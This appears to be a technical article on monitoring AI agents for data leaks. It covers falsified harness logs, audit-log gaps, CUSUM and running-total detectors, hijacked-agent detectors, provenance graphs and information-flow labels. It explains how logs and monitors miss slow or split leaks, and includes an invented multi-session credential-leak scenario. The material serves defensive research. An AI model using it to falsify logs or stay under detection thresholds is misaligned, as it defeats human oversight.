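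The agent's log is identical in both histories, so any method that uses only this log must give the same verdict in both. Because "supported" would be wrong in the second history and "contradicted" in the first, a method that must never give a false verdict has to return "undecidable".

Signing the log doesn't show that it is complete. A signature shows who supplied the entries, and the same entries carry the same valid signature whether an event was left out or never happened. An outside checkpoint of those entries would also be identical in both cases. Numbering the entries reveals a gap only if the event received a number before someone removed it.

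The proof assumes that the agent could have taken an unrecorded action, and a company can try to make this impossible. Kodathala's gateway can optionally run with the agent on an internal network whose only exit is the gateway. The gateway can also hold the passwords for outside services, so an agent that bypasses it has no credentials to use. The agent could then send an unlogged email only if the gateway or the network barrier had a fault. This setup gives stronger evidence that the log is complete than any signature on the agent's own log, although the auditor still has to check that the barrier was in place for the whole period.

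Zhao also assumes, generously, that the agent and the team running it may omit actions but never record one that did not happen. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (Brömme, 2026) reports that investigators of the July 2026 incident, in which OpenAI agents attacked the AI platform Hugging Face, documented attempts to falsify or delete records and limited successful demonstrations of faked tool calls.

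### Twenty-eight falsified logs

Zhao cites an experiment from *Hearsay* (Dai, Yang and colleagues, 2026) that tested both omissions and invented entries in the logs that agent harnesses write. A harness is the software that passes messages between a model and its tools, and it usually writes the log too.

The researchers modified aider, an open-source coding assistant, so that its harness falsified the log as it ran. In 14 runs the log omitted the model's reply. In another 14 it included an invented statement that the model had rerun the tests and all had passed. A hash chain over the log still verified in all 28 runs, as it was bound to, because the harness computed the hashes after deciding what to write.

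Meanwhile, a process outside the harness kept a second log, which Dai and colleagues call a ledger. It recorded every message between the harness and the model, every program that started and every file that changed. The researchers then checked each log against the other. They found the 14 omissions by looking for messages that appeared only in the ledger, and the 14 inventions by looking for text that appeared only in the harness's log. The same comparison found no discrepancies in 28 unaltered aider logs.

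Dai and colleagues call this their easiest test, because they knew in advance what was false. For a harder test, they ran three harnesses with a model from another company and fixed the comparison rules before the logs existed. They removed, changed or added one item in each of 66 logs. The comparison found 64 of the 66 alterations, and its search for invented or changed items raised no false alarms on 84 unaltered logs.

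In a third test, with logs in five formats, the comparison found 109 of 115 changes. When it ignored only the harmless differences the researchers had named beforehand, it wrongly flagged 37 of the 115 unaltered logs. After they read some of the logs and added more exceptions, it wrongly flagged one. A company that compares its own logs should therefore expect many false alarms at first, particularly when it adds an agent with a new log format.

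The comparison also uncovered a fault that nobody had planted in SWE-agent, a widely used coding agent. Run exactly as released, SWE-agent left 37 of 412 tool calls out of its saved logs. The harness had refused most of these calls, for instance because the model had sent several at once, and it recorded neither the calls nor its refusals. Refused calls don't move data, so the missing entries were mainly failed attempts. These still matter for leak detection, because an agent that keeps trying to open a password file deserves attention even if it never succeeds.

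Reading one log carefully was a poor substitute for comparing it with a second log. When Dai and colleagues gave Claude Sonnet 5 single logs without the ledger, it flagged 49% of the altered logs and 5% of the unaltered ones. Human readers, deciding by majority, flagged 37% and 10%. Missing replies were especially hard to notice. When asked directly whether each log was faithful, the model said no for 7 of the 14 logs with a missing reply and 5 of the 13 faithful ones. A monitor that reads only the agent's log is likely to have the same difficulty.

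The second log also has to record actions, because a false result can enter the conversation itself. In one set of runs, the researchers made the harness report failed software tests as passed to both the model and the first log. The second log's copy of the messages contained the same false result, but its record of how the test program ended exposed all 11 cases in which tests had failed. For a leak, the equivalent is a mail server or network record of what left the company.

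These were coding tasks of at most seven minutes. The design also depends on an honest operator, since one who controls both logs could falsify both. As a partial check, Dai and colleagues retrieved the model provider's stored copies of all 708 model calls in the 84 runs, and every copy matched the ledger. With two other harnesses, the provider returned copies of only about three quarters of the calls. The provider's copies also don't include an email that a script sends without calling the model again.

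Few companies will get a second log by default. Dai and colleagues used a language model to examine 16 agent frameworks, and it found none whose records an outsider could check without trusting the framework. A model from another company also found none.

### Matching three logs

Zhao's invented email case combines logs from the agent, the authorisation server and the mail gateway. The company says that "a person approves every external email". Zhao first restates this as a claim an auditor can check: before the agent sent any email with an attachment outside the company in March, a signed-in person must have approved that recipient and that attachment.

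The table shows what the logs contain for each of the four emails. The names beginning with "tx" are correlation identifiers, except for tx-31, which is only a label for an email whose identifier is missing from the agent's log.

| Email | Agent's log | Authorisation server's log | Mail gateway's log | Finding |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| tx-19 | Names a grant | Earlier approval for the same recipient and attachment | Matching delivery | Meets the policy |
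| tx-23 | Only a click in the agent's chat window | Complete, with no matching grant | Matching delivery | Breaks the policy |
| tx-31 | No grant or identifier | Lost for that hour | Delivery | Undecidable |
| Fourth email | No entry | No matching grant | Delivery from the agent's account | Undecidable |

For tx-19, the auditor compares the recipient and the attachment's fingerprint across all three logs and checks that the approval came before the delivery. These checks cover only this email, so they don't support the company's claim about the whole month.

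For tx-23, the missing grant counts as a violation only because the server's log is complete for the period in which someone could have issued one. An auditor can't infer a violation from the missing grant for tx-31, because someone may have issued a grant that the log doesn't include.

It is unclear who used the agent's account for the fourth email. The auditor could probably find out if the gateway had recorded which program connected to it.

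Zhao allows three verdicts on the claim as a whole. The claim is "supported" if evidence shows that the records include every relevant email and that each one met the policy. It is "contradicted" if even one violation is proven. Otherwise it is "undecidable", and the auditor should name the record that would have settled it. The March claim is contradicted because tx-23 is a proven violation. If someone had properly approved tx-23, the claim would be undecidable until the auditor resolved the other two emails.

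A company can automate part of this work. The following query lists deliveries for which the agent's log has no entry with the same recipient and attachment:

```sql
SELECT g.time, g.recipient, g.attachment_hash
FROM gateway_log AS g
LEFT JOIN agent_log AS a
  ON a.recipient = g.recipient
 AND a.sent_hash = g.attachment_hash
WHERE g.sender = 'deploy-agent'
  AND a.session IS NULL
```

The same query with the two logs swapped finds emails that the agent recorded but the gateway never delivered. Some of these will be harmless, such as messages that the gateway rejected.

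The query misses an unlogged second email when an agent sends the same file to the same person twice, because the one log entry matches both deliveries. Adding a correlation identifier to each delivery fixes this, as does allowing each entry to match only one delivery. Dai and colleagues found a similar problem when they asked a model that knew their comparison rules to invent entries that would pass. Of its 100 attempts, 35 passed the original comparison because one genuine item could match more than one entry. After they tightened the matching, the comparison caught all 50 attempts in a second round but raised a few false alarms on one log format.

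### Missing file reads in Copilot

A commercial audit log can be incomplete even if nobody has tampered with it. In August 2025, Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You* disclosed that Microsoft 365 Copilot could read and summarise a file without the audit log recording the access. Pistachio, which sells security training and monitoring, found the problem while generating log entries to test a product, so the gap could occur by accident. An employee could also have used it to read files unnoticed before leaving for a competitor.

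The gap was particularly hard to notice because the audit log had no second entry to compare with the Copilot record that omitted the file. When Copilot opens a file for a user, Microsoft's log is meant to contain a Copilot interaction that names the file. It does not also contain the ordinary file-access event that appears when the user opens the file directly. Pistachio considers leaving out that event sensible, since the user did not open the file.

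According to Pistachio, it reported the problem in early July 2025, and Microsoft rated it "important", one level below "critical", and scheduled a full fix for 17 August. Microsoft declined to issue a CVE, a public identifier for a security flaw, because customers did not need to install anything, and told Pistachio that it had no plans to inform them. Pistachio also says that the chief technology officer of Zenity, another security company, had disclosed the same problem a year earlier.

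A fix changes what the log records from then on, but it cannot restore reads that the log omitted. In an investigation of a leak from early 2025, a file's absence from Copilot's records is therefore weak evidence that nobody used Copilot to read it. Microsoft's reason for not issuing a CVE makes sense if the purpose of a CVE is to get customers to install an update, but companies that rely on old logs also need to know that reads may be missing.

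According to Microsoft's documentation, the audit record now names the files that Copilot accesses, but documentation shows only what a log should contain. A company can test its own log, as Asböck did for administrative changes, by having an agent read known files and checking that each read appears. If 100 test reads all appear, the log probably misses fewer than 3% of such reads, because a log that missed 3% would have only about a 5% chance of recording all 100 (0.97 to the power of 100). This estimate applies only to reads like those tested, so the log could still have gaps under other conditions.

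### What a detector can infer from a clean log

When a detector finds nothing suspicious, the result applies only to the recorded events. If the agent wrote the only log, an auditor can conclude that the log contains nothing the detector recognises as a leak. If the log also has a verified hash chain with an outside checkpoint, the auditor can conclude that nobody has changed the entries up to that checkpoint since it was made. Neither finding is evidence that the agent logged all its actions.

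Like sampling, missing entries reduce a detector's recall. Suppose a detector finds 80% of leaks in complete logs and needs one record from each of two sessions to recognise a leak. If the log misses 5% of events at random, the chance that it holds both records is about 90%, and recall falls to about 72%. If the detector needs one record from each of six sessions, recall falls to about 59%. Deliberate omissions would reduce recall further, because someone hiding a leak would leave out the records the detector needs.

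If the agent's log matches an independent one, an auditor can draw a stronger conclusion, but only about the channel that both cover. Suppose the mail gateway handles all outgoing email and every delivery in March matches an approved entry in the agent's log. The company can then reasonably say that the agent sent no unapproved attachments by email that month. To say the same about web uploads or shared folders, it would need a second record of those too. Approval also doesn't show that an attachment was safe to send, since the approver may not have noticed what it contained.

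A detector should therefore raise an alert whenever the logs don't match. In Zhao's case, a detector that searched only the agent's log for suspicious patterns would never examine the fourth email.

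## How do limits and running totals find slow leaks?

The simplest detectors count what an agent sends and raise an alarm when the count passes a limit. Agents also send data for legitimate reasons, so the limit has to be higher than this ordinary traffic. These detectors therefore miss a leak slow enough to stay below the limit.

### From a session limit to a 30-day total

A per-session limit caps how much an agent can send in one session, for instance at 50 customer records. This stops an agent from exporting the whole customer table at once. It doesn't stop an agent from sending 100 records over 20 sessions, five at a time, because the count resets each session.

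A sliding window avoids that reset. Each day, the detector adds up everything the agent sent in the last 30 days and compares the total with a limit. This works better than a total for each calendar month, which would cut a leak that runs from the 20th to the 10th in half. The following query computes the sliding total from a table with one row per user, destination and day:

```sql
SELECT user_id, destination, day,
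  SUM(records) OVER (
    PARTITION BY user_id, destination
    ORDER BY day
    RANGE BETWEEN INTERVAL '29' DAY PRECEDING
              AND CURRENT ROW) AS total_30d
FROM daily_totals
```

The PARTITION BY line determines which records count together. Here, one user's transfers to three addresses produce three separate totals, so the company also needs a total for each user across all destinations. Banks must also choose which cash payments to add together.

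The smallest leak a running total can reveal depends on the length of its window. Suppose an agent normally sends 20 sensitive records a day with a standard deviation of 5, so on about two days in three it sends between 15 and 25. It then starts leaking 5 more records a day. If the daily counts vary independently, a normal seven-day total averages 140 with a standard deviation of about 13, and a limit three standard deviations above the average is about 180. The leak raises the average only to 175, so it can continue for weeks without an alarm.

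Normal 30-day totals average 600 records with a standard deviation of about 27, so the limit is 682. The leak typically pushes the total past this limit after 16 or 17 days, when about 80 records have been lost. But the longer window is worse at finding sudden leaks. A single loss of 50 records would usually push the seven-day total over its limit, but not the 30-day total.

### The cumulative-sum test

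Factories use the cumulative-sum test, or CUSUM, to notice small but lasting changes in a production process. It keeps a running total of how far each day's count exceeds the normal level:

S_t = max(0, S_{t−1} + x_t − μ − k)

In this formula, x_t is the number of records sent on day t, μ is the normal daily average, and k is an allowance for harmless variation. The sum S starts at zero, and the detector raises an alarm when S exceeds a threshold h. On a normal day, subtracting k tends to lower S. The maximum keeps S from falling below zero, because otherwise a few quiet months could make it so negative that a later leak would not raise it above h.

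For the agent that normally sends 20 records a day, suitable values are k = 2.5 and h = 25. The table shows invented data for ten days in which the agent leaks 5 extra records a day.

| Day | Records sent | Records − 22.5 | Sum S |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 19 | −3.5 | 0 |
| 2 | 27 | +4.5 | 4.5 |
| 3 | 24 | +1.5 | 6.0 |
| 4 | 30 | +7.5 | 13.5 |
| 5 | 21 | −1.5 | 12.0 |
| 6 | 26 | +3.5 | 15.5 |
| 7 | 23 | +0.5 | 16.0 |
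| 8 | 28 | +5.5 | 21.5 |
| 9 | 22 | −0.5 | 21.0 |
| 10 | 30 | +7.5 | 28.5 |

The sum passes 25 on day 10, after the agent has leaked 50 records. A fixed limit of 35 records a day, three standard deviations above the average, would not have raised an alarm, because the agent never sent more than 30 in a day.

Ten days is also close to the average. The textbook chapter *Time Weighted Control Charts in Phase II* calculates the average time both methods take when k is half a standard deviation and h is five. The next table converts its results into records for this agent. The row for 1.25 records uses figures from *Using ARL (Average Run Length) to determine the performance*, a blog post by the statistics software company JMP.

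| Leaked records a day | CUSUM: days to alarm | CUSUM: records gone | Limit of 35: days to alarm | Limit of 35: records gone |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 (false alarm) | 465 | – | 370 | – |
| 1.25 | 139 | 174 | 281 | 351 |
| 2.5 | 38 | 95 | 155 | 388 |
| 5 | 10.4 | 52 | 44 | 219 |
| 10 | 4.0 | 40 | 6.3 | 63 |
| 15 | 2.6 | 39 | 2.0 | 30 |

These figures also count alarms for unusually low totals, which don't matter here. A company that watches only for increases would get about half as many false alarms. With CUSUM, that is roughly one every 930 days per agent. The smallest leaks would also take somewhat longer to trigger an alarm, especially with the fixed limit.

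The allowance k cancels a leak of 2.5 records a day, so the sum reaches the threshold only through random variation. Below that rate, the sum tends to fall. If the agent leaks 1.25 records a day for a month and then stops, the chance of an alarm is at most about one in five.

The fixed limit is slightly faster for the largest leak in the table. The textbook chapter notes that engineers often run both tests for this reason. It also describes an alternative, the exponentially weighted moving average, in which each day's value is, say, 20% of the new count and 80% of the previous value. With suitable limits, this average takes almost exactly as long as CUSUM to detect a leak of 5 records a day, so the choice between the two matters little.

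The choice of the allowance k matters more. According to Bourazas (2026), in *Statistical Process Control*, the best k is half the change the test should find. When counts follow a bell curve, a day's evidence for a leak of δ records, compared with no leak, is proportional to x_t − μ − δ/2, so CUSUM with k = δ/2 adds up the evidence for a leak of that size. A smaller k makes the test more sensitive to small leaks but slower to react to large ones.

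After fixing an agent that leaked, investigators can also give the sum a head start by restarting S at 12.5 instead of zero, in case the fix did not work. If the agent still leaks 5 records a day, the average time to an alarm falls from 10.4 days to 6.35, and false alarms become only slightly more frequent.

CUSUM needs very little storage, since the detector keeps one number per agent and can continue after the company has deleted the daily records.

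### Comparison with an agent's past and its peers

The company has to estimate the average, μ, and the standard deviation, usually from the agent's own history. With 30 days of data, the estimate of μ will be at least 1.25 records too low for about one agent in twelve. For those agents, CUSUM treats normal traffic as a leak of that size and raises a false alarm every few months.

History is also misleading if the leak began before the company started measuring. If an assistant has sent a password file to an outside service since its first day, its profile includes this as normal behavior. A baseline that updates every day comes to include later leaks too. If μ is the average of the last 30 days, a steady leak of 5 records a day raises it from 20 to 25 within a month, and the leak no longer counts as unusual in the test.

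Comparing the agent with others that do the same job can expose such a leak. If 19 support agents each send about 20 records a day and the twentieth sends 40, the difference is visible however long it has existed. The comparison is less useful when a shared instruction causes the leak. In the NordLayer case, the project's instructions pointed the assistant to the file with the passwords, so every assistant working on that project might have read it.

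A difference from peers may also have a harmless cause, such as a larger customer. *ProvAgent* (2026) describes a system for investigating attacks on computers, in which a language model compares each suspicious item with its most similar counterpart and with harmless items of the same type. The model is instructed to report an anomaly only if the differing behaviour is itself suspicious.

*Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (Canale, 2026) tested behaviour profiles like those in UEBA tools on a simulated company with 200 people and 23 software services. None of the profiled users were language-model agents. The profiles found 56% of the attacks but raised 317 false alarms a day. When limited to ten false alarms a day, they found 7% of the attacks.

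Every detector that worked within such a budget missed bulk data theft that appeared in only one log, like reading a whole database table or copying unusual amounts of data between sites. Canale then added a separate baseline for each combination of account, table and hour of the day, and a similar one for each copying route. These baselines found 29 of the 39 missed cases without adding false alarms. Versions that ignored the hour raised alarms on nightly backups and missed 12 of the 14 copying cases.

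Canale designed these baselines after seeing which attacks had escaped detection, so they would probably do less well on new attacks. Still, the result suggests that such baselines could partly help with agents whose normal activity is very broad. Such an agent may rarely open the payroll table, and a baseline for its use of that table would reveal a small increase.

### How much could have left without an alarm?

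The average delays in the CUSUM table assume that the agent leaks the same amount every day, but CUSUM also gives an upper bound that holds for any pattern. If it has raised no alarm, the agent has sent at most n(μ + k) + h records in any n consecutive days. This is because S has not exceeded h, and S is always at least as large as the sum of x_t − μ − k over any stretch of days up to that point.

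Over 30 days, the agent can send up to 30 × 22.5 + 25 = 700 records unnoticed. It normally sends 600 in that time, so a leak can add about 100, or more if the agent's legitimate traffic is low. With a fixed limit of 35 a day, the agent could send up to 1,050 records unnoticed.

*Practical Comprehensive Bounds on Surreptitious Communication Over DNS* (Paxson, Christodorescu and colleagues, 2013) develops a bound of this kind for a channel that most companies can't close. The Domain Name System (DNS) translates names such as www.example.com into the numeric addresses that computers use. Whoever runs a domain receives lookups for names under it, so a compromised computer can send data out by hiding it in those lookups. A single lookup can carry as little as one bit, too little for anyone to recognise as part of a leak.

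Paxson and colleagues therefore calculated the most information each computer could have sent to each domain in a day. They listed the names, types and times of the lookups and compressed each list with several standard programs, such as gzip. Because the compression is reversible, the compressed size can't be smaller than the information hidden in the list. They kept the smallest result for each list and added these together. In tests with known hidden files, the estimates were 5–11% above the true amount.

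The limit was 4 kilobytes per computer and domain per day. In networks where individual computers could be distinguished, analysts had to investigate an average of one or two domains a week. This number depended partly on a list of domains that analysts had already checked. At an industrial laboratory, the method flagged 16 domains in the first week but about two in a typical later week. Across 230 billion lookups from all the networks studied, it found 59 confirmed hidden channels. Two belonged to staff at a national laboratory who had set them up to get free internet access at Wi-Fi hotspots.

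Simply adding up the length of the names, with the same 4-kilobyte limit, produced 200 times as many alerts. Most of that volume came from harmless lookups. Many of these were repeated, and repeated data compresses well. Lowering the limit from 4,096 bytes to 256 would have given analysts about 50 times as many domains to inspect.

Data can still leak without exceeding the limit. Four kilobytes a day adds up to about 1.5 megabytes a year, and the limit applies separately to each combination of computer and domain. Paxson and colleagues acknowledge that data split among several domains or computers could stay below every limit. For data split among domains, they suggest limiting each computer's total across all of them.

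The method should work best for agents on channels where legitimate messages are short and repetitive, such as status updates or web requests. It would be of little use for email. An agent that writes thousands of words a day to customers could hide far more than 4 kilobytes in them, so any valid bound would be too large to help. Counting what the agent has read can give a tighter bound. If, according to the log, it opened only 40 customer records this month, and it had no other source for them, it cannot have leaked more than 40.

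A bound on new information also misses repeated transfers of the same data. In the NordLayer case, the second copy of the same file gave the outside service almost nothing new, so a compression-based measure would count the ten transfers as little more than one.

### Disclosure budgets

A disclosure budget is a limit the company sets on how much data an agent may send out in a given period. When the agent's running total reaches the limit, the agent has to stop or ask a person. For example, the company might let a support agent send up to 200 customer records per quarter to any one outside company.

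The company can also set the budget per dataset. If at most 1% of the customer table may leave in a year, all agents and users share that 1%, so dividing the work among ten agents doesn't raise the limit. This works only if the data keeps its label when an agent rewrites it.

Differential privacy, a mathematical method for publishing statistics about people, uses a formal version of this idea. Each answer adds to a running total of privacy loss, and the system stops answering when the total reaches a limit. The method's privacy guarantee relies on adding random noise to each answer, so it doesn't apply to an agent that has to email a customer's exact address.

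An ordinary budget can't distinguish legitimate disclosures from leaks either. Agents use up a tight budget during a busy month and someone raises it, while data can leak within the unspent part of a generous one. The budget still limits the damage, which helps when a company doesn't trust its detector.

A greater difficulty is that volume is a poor measure of sensitivity. A password or access key may be only a few dozen characters long and still open a database with a million records. About 100 keys of 40 characters each would fit within Paxson and colleagues' daily limit of 4 kilobytes. The agent in the CUSUM example could send one key in place of a customer record without changing its count.

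One remedy is to weight the count, so that a customer's name adds one point and a credit card number adds 50. The weights are partly arbitrary. Credentials probably need a separate rule that raises an alarm whenever even one leaves the company, but the software then needs content matching to recognise them.

Mosaic attacks cause a related problem, because the value of the answers depends on how they combine. A limit on the number of distinct facts a user obtains about the company's network would reflect the risk better than a limit on bytes.

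### Nine real alarms in a thousand

Suppose a company's agents run 100,000 sessions a day, 10 of which are part of leaks. With 90% recall and a 1% false-positive rate, a detector raises about 1,009 alarms a day, 9 of them real. At ten minutes per alarm, checking them takes 21 people working eight-hour days.

The share of alarms that are real is the detector's precision. When a fraction π of sessions is harmful, the precision is

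πR / (πR + (1 − π)F)

where R is the recall and F the false-positive rate. With π = 0.0001, even perfect recall would raise the precision only from 0.89% to 0.99%. To make half the alarms real at 90% recall, the company would have to reduce the false-positive rate from 1% to about 0.009%.

It is more useful to compare detectors by how many attacks each finds without raising more false alarms than analysts can handle. Canale set this limit at ten a day. Simple rules that matched single events found 73% of attacks while raising 4,640 false alarms a day, but only 1% when limited to 100 false alarms. With a limit of ten, one of the better systems found 62% of attacks, but only 32% when Canale made the simulated company ten times larger, because there was ten times as much harmless activity that could raise false alarms and the limit stayed the same.

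The advantage of running totals is that they require fewer tests than checking every session. If 2,000 agents run the 100,000 sessions and each agent has one CUSUM with a false alarm every 930 days, the company gets about two false alarms a day. This advantage disappears if the company divides the totals too finely. With separate totals for 50 destinations per agent, it would run 100,000 tests and get about 108 false alarms a day. Both figures are optimistic because they depend on daily counts being independent and following a bell curve. An agent may instead send nothing for a week and then 200 records on the day of a product launch.

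### Tests on agents' tool calls

The survey *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (2026) distinguishes detectors that use explicit signals, such as the structure and timing of a run, from detectors that interpret what the agent was trying to do. Counts and baselines belong to the first type. *TraceAegis* (2025), for example, uses gateway logs to learn an agent's normal order of tool calls and rules about its behaviour, then flags runs that depart from them. It doesn't need the agent's prompts or reasoning, which a company often can't obtain, but it would have little to detect in a slow leak that uses the usual tools in the usual order.

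Published results for such detectors are often better than a company should expect to get. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki, 2026) reviewed eleven evaluations. In test sets that mixed harmful and harmless samples, attacks or anomalies made up 16% to 86% of the samples. None of the evaluations tested how results would change if attacks were rarer.

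Abbasi and colleagues then trained their own detectors on AgentDrift, a set of synthetic agent sessions, some of them hijacked by hostile instructions in tool results. One detector used the number of calls to each tool and ten general features, such as session length and the variety of tools. It gave a randomly chosen hijacked session a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless one 88% of the time. At a threshold where it found 77% of the hijacked sessions, it also flagged 19% of the harmless ones. If 2% of sessions were hijacked, only 7.6% of its alarms would be real, and if 0.1% were hijacked, that share would fall to 0.4%.

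A detector that also used the order of the tool calls did better. At the 2% rate, 24% of its alarms were real, but it found only 68% of the hijacked sessions.

The kind of harmless work in the test mattered almost as much as the rarity of attacks. The first detector flagged 12% of ordinary harmless sessions and 39% of those that AgentDrift includes as difficult cases. At a 2% attack rate, its precision would be 11.7% if all the harmless sessions were ordinary and 3.9% if all were difficult. A company whose agents routinely do unusual work can therefore expect more false alarms than a standard test suggests.

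None of the detectors trained on AgentDrift did better than chance on AgentDojo, a set of recorded agent runs. The same types of detector worked on AgentDojo when Abbasi and colleagues trained them on it, partly because the test was easy. Five fixed attack phrases appeared in 99.6% of its hijacked sessions and in none of the harmless ones, so a text-based detector could succeed by learning the phrases.

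A second check can reduce false alarms. In *LumiMAS* (2025), a detector for multi-agent systems passes only the logs it flags to a language model, which re-examines them. This cut the false-positive rate by about 60% on average but slightly reduced recall. In the company with 100,000 sessions, the same reduction would leave about 400 false alarms a day alongside at most 9 real ones.

All of these tests looked for faults or attacks within individual runs. They show that ordinary variation between sessions produces many false alarms, but they don't measure how well a monthly total would find a slow leak.

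### Why an agent's normal behaviour shifts

A baseline is useful only while the agent works in roughly the same way. Agents can change overnight. A new model may read five files for a task where the old one read two, and one sentence added to the standing instructions may lead every agent to attach its sources. The work also changes, for instance when a finance team closes its accounts at the end of a quarter. Zhang and colleagues also list refreshed search indexes, changed settings and feedback loops as causes of drift.

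An update that increases an agent's legitimate traffic can look exactly like a leak. If traffic rises from 20 records a day to 25, CUSUM will raise an alarm after about ten days, just as it would if the agent were leaking 5 records a day. If 500 agents receive the update together, the company may get hundreds of false alarms in the same two weeks.

New tools cause similar problems for trained detectors. Abbasi and colleagues simulated unfamiliar tools by hiding tool names from their detectors. With every name hidden, the false-positive rate rose from 19% to 66% for the detector based on tool counts and from 4.5% to 74% for the one based on the order of calls. Hiding some names during training as well kept the call-order detector's false-positive rate between 5% and 7%, but that detector still became worse at telling hijacked sessions from harmless ones.

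Comparing agents helps distinguish an update from a leak in a single agent, because an update should affect all of them. But an update can also cause a leak, and resetting every baseline afterwards would make that leak part of normal behaviour. It is safer to run the old and new versions on the same tasks first and check what additional data the new version sends, and to whom. The company can then raise μ by the amount it has accepted as legitimate, and CUSUM will still count the rest.

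## How can data be followed from source to destination?

A running total shows how much an agent has sent, but not where the data came from. In the six-session plan, the agent sends only about 4 kilobytes, but the data comes from a file of database credentials. A detector can identify the source by tracing the logged steps back to the file, or by recognising the file's content in what the agent sends.

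### A graph of the six sessions

A provenance graph shows where data went. Its nodes are things that hold or handle data, such as files, messages, memory entries, sessions and outside addresses. Its edges are reads, writes and sends, and each edge points in the direction the data moved. Security teams already build such graphs from operating-system audit logs. According to *PIDSMaker* (2026), which describes a toolkit for detecting intrusions with these graphs, they can grow to millions of nodes and edges. Since operating-system logs don't identify the agent or request behind an action, *Cross-Layer Semantic Flow Reconstruction for Attack Detection in Agentic Systems* (2026) adds agents, their messages and their tool requests to the graph.

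The next table lists the edges for the six-session plan, using the same invented session and file names as the log records above. It leaves out the first two sessions, in which the user only learned what to ask for next.

| Order | From | To | Action |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | config/database.yml | s-92 (session 3) | Read |
| 2 | config/database.yml | s-98 (session 4) | Read |
| 3 | s-98 | docs/db-summary.md | Write |
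| 4 | docs/db-summary.md | s-105 (session 5) | Read |
| 5 | s-105 | jobs/backup-17.txt | Write |
| 6 | jobs/backup-17.txt | s-131 (session 6) | Read |
| 7 | s-131 | intake@monitor.example | Send |

Edge 6 relies on the fingerprint match between the two log records. With the edges in a database table, this query finds every path from a protected file to an outside address:

```sql
WITH RECURSIVE trail AS (
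  SELECT dst AS node, seq, src || ' > ' || dst AS path
  FROM edges
  WHERE src IN (SELECT name FROM protected_files)
  UNION ALL
  SELECT e.dst, e.seq, t.path || ' > ' || e.dst
  FROM trail AS t
  JOIN edges AS e ON e.src = t.node AND e.seq > t.seq
)
SELECT path FROM trail
WHERE node IN (SELECT address FROM outside_addresses)
```

The query starts from the protected files and repeatedly follows every edge that leaves a node it has reached. Here it returns one path:

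```
config/database.yml > s-98 > docs/db-summary.md > s-105
  > jobs/backup-17.txt > s-131 > intake@monitor.example
```

The condition on `seq` keeps the steps in order. Without it, a session in which the agent emailed a supplier before it read the settings file would look like a leak. The agent also read the file in session 3, but that branch ends there because the agent stored nothing. An investigator who begins with a suspicious email can search backward from the address to every file the email could have drawn on.

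### How certain is each link?

If an agent reads 12 files in a session and writes three, the graph contains 36 possible links, and perhaps only a few are real. *Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* (2026) points out that a log of tool calls records the steps and their times but not which output fed which input. In 12 of 40 successful attacks in its tests, the agent had also recalled harmless facts before sending anything, so the order of events was not enough to identify which memory was responsible.

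In the six-session path, an auditor has to infer only the step inside s-98, because fingerprints confirm the later steps. *ExecWeave* (2026) describes a tool that stores the supporting evidence with each edge and marks the inferred edges. Both practices are worth copying, because people tend to read a line between two nodes as proof.

### Labels that pass from inputs to outputs

Instead of searching for paths afterwards, a company can attach a sensitivity label to each piece of data and have software update the labels as the agent works. Suppose public data has level 0, internal data level 1 and secret data level 2. An output gets the highest level among its inputs:

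L(output) = max(L(input₁), …, L(inputₙ))

The agent may send data only if L(data) ≤ L(destination), where L is the secrecy level. If it writes the summary from the secret settings file (level 2) and an internal deployment guide (level 1), the summary takes the higher level, max(2, 1) = 2. The encoded version also has level 2. An outside address may receive only level 0, so sending the encoded version there breaks the rule. The level doesn't depend on the wording, so unlike a fingerprint, it survives the summary and the encoding.

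Some labels can't be ranked against each other. A payroll file isn't more or less secret than a legal file, and a memo that draws on both should go only to people who may see both. The general rule therefore replaces "max" with ⊔, which gives the lowest label that covers both inputs.

Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, give each value a secrecy label c and a trust label i, and combine them like this:

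(c₁, i₁) ⊔ (c₂, i₂) = (c₁ ⊔ c₂, i₁ ⊓ i₂)

The symbol ⊓ works the other way, giving the highest trust level that both inputs meet. The result is at least as secret as the most secret input and no more trusted than the least trusted one. The trust label guards against prompt injection, for instance by not letting text from an unknown web page determine who receives a payment.

SPA also labels decisions. Suppose an agent emails a supplier only if a confidential contract contains a termination clause. The email may contain nothing from the contract, but its arrival reveals that the clause exists. SPA therefore adds the contract's label to everything the agent does as a result of checking for the clause.

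### When the session ends

If the labels exist only in the agent's working context, they are lost when that context ends, so they have to be stored with the data. Each kind of store has a weak point.

| Store | Where to keep the label | How the data can lose it |
|---|---|---|
| Agent memory | In a field beside each entry | The agent condenses several entries into a new one |
| Shared file | In the gateway's records, under the file's fingerprint | Someone edits the file without going through the gateway |
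| Database row | In an extra column | A query combines many rows and returns only the result |

Many agents store short summaries of past work instead of full records. *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (2026) describes how summarizing loses the source of a memory. It proposes that the platform keep the source, trust level and history of changes with each memory. SPA stores every result with its label and restores the label when a later request retrieves the result. The planning model receives only a description of the stored data.

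*MemLineage* (Ouyang and Hou, 2026) signs each memory and records which earlier memories it came from. It also estimates how strongly each old memory influenced the new one, and passes on a warning label only if the estimate exceeds a threshold. In a simulation of repeated summarizing, the estimate starts at 0.9 and falls by 30% with each summary, to about 0.22 by the fifth. A threshold of 0.3 would keep the label after one summary but lose it by the fifth, so Ouyang and Hou recommend a threshold of at most 0.1 for chains of that length.

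In Ouyang and Hou's main test, MemLineage blocked all three types of attack, while signatures alone blocked one. However, the test used scripted behaviour instead of a live language model. MemLineage's labels mark untrusted content rather than secrets. The same records could carry a secrecy label, but Ouyang and Hou leave leaks of private memories to other defences.

### Agent systems that enforce labels

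FIDES, described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), is one of two systems from that year usually used for comparison. It keeps one label for everything the planning model has seen, and checks each tool call against this label and the labels of the call's arguments. To keep the model's label low, FIDES can hide a result in a variable, which the model passes on without reading. FIDES guarantees that data the agent explicitly passes along obeys the policy. In the paper's tests, this protection caused a "modest loss in utility".

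CaMeL, by Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, divides the work between two models. One turns the user's request into a program and never receives tool results. The other processes untrusted text but cannot change the program. CaMeL tags each value with its source and permitted recipients, and checks these tags before a tool call. Girrens and Wang point out that the guarantee this provides depends on someone having written a correct policy for each tool.

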